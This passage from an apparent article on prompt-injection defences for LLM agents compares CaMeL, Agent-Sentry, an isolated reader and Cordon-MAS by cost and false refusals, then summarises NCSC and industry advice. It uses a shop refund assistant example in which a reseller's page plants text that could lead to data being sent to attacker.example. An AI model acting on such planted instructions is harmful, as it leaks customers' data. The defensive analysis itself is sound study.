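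| CaMeL with rules | Planted text can't add tool calls | Several times the running time | Nearly half of the banking tasks it completes without rules |
| Agent-Sentry | None | About 0.07 seconds per run on average with the trained classifier | 13–31% of harmless runs on the older benchmarks |
| L3M's isolated reader | 1.58 bits per call | A model call per question | Any answer outside the fixed choices |
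| Cordon-MAS | The answering model never sees the documents | 2.8 times the cost | 40% of clean questions refused |

These figures come from different tasks and models, so they can't be used to rank the defences. They do suggest that the strict defences suit predictable tasks where a wrong action would be harmful. The shop's refund assistant is a good fit because it needs only a few tools and destinations. The same defences would restrict a research agent much more, because it visits unfamiliar sites all day.

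### Official and industry advice

In the National Cyber Security Centre post, David C advises developers to concentrate on safeguards that don't rely on a language model, instead of only trying to keep malicious text out. The post also recommends that when a model processes someone's text, its privileges should drop to that person's level, a rule that came from a discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista. Under this rule, the shop's assistant couldn't read a customer's order while the reseller's page is in its context, because the reseller isn't allowed to read it.

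David C still supports marking untrusted text to make attacks harder, but warns against relying on lists of known attack phrases and against products that claim to "stop" prompt injection. David C also recommends logging the model's inputs, outputs and tool calls, because an attacker will probably need several attempts and the failed calls may reveal the attack. A blocked request to attacker.example should therefore alert the shop's staff, who can look for the document that caused it.

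Costa and colleagues at Microsoft similarly argue that model training and filters give no strong assurance, and that business, banking and medical uses need firm rules. Researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind found scanners useful but limited in their joint 2025 study of adaptive attacks.

None of these sources tests scanning, labels, isolated readers and egress controls together, so the advice is based on how the parts work and on tests of them separately. David C adds that a system may not be a good use for a language model if the remaining risk is unacceptable.
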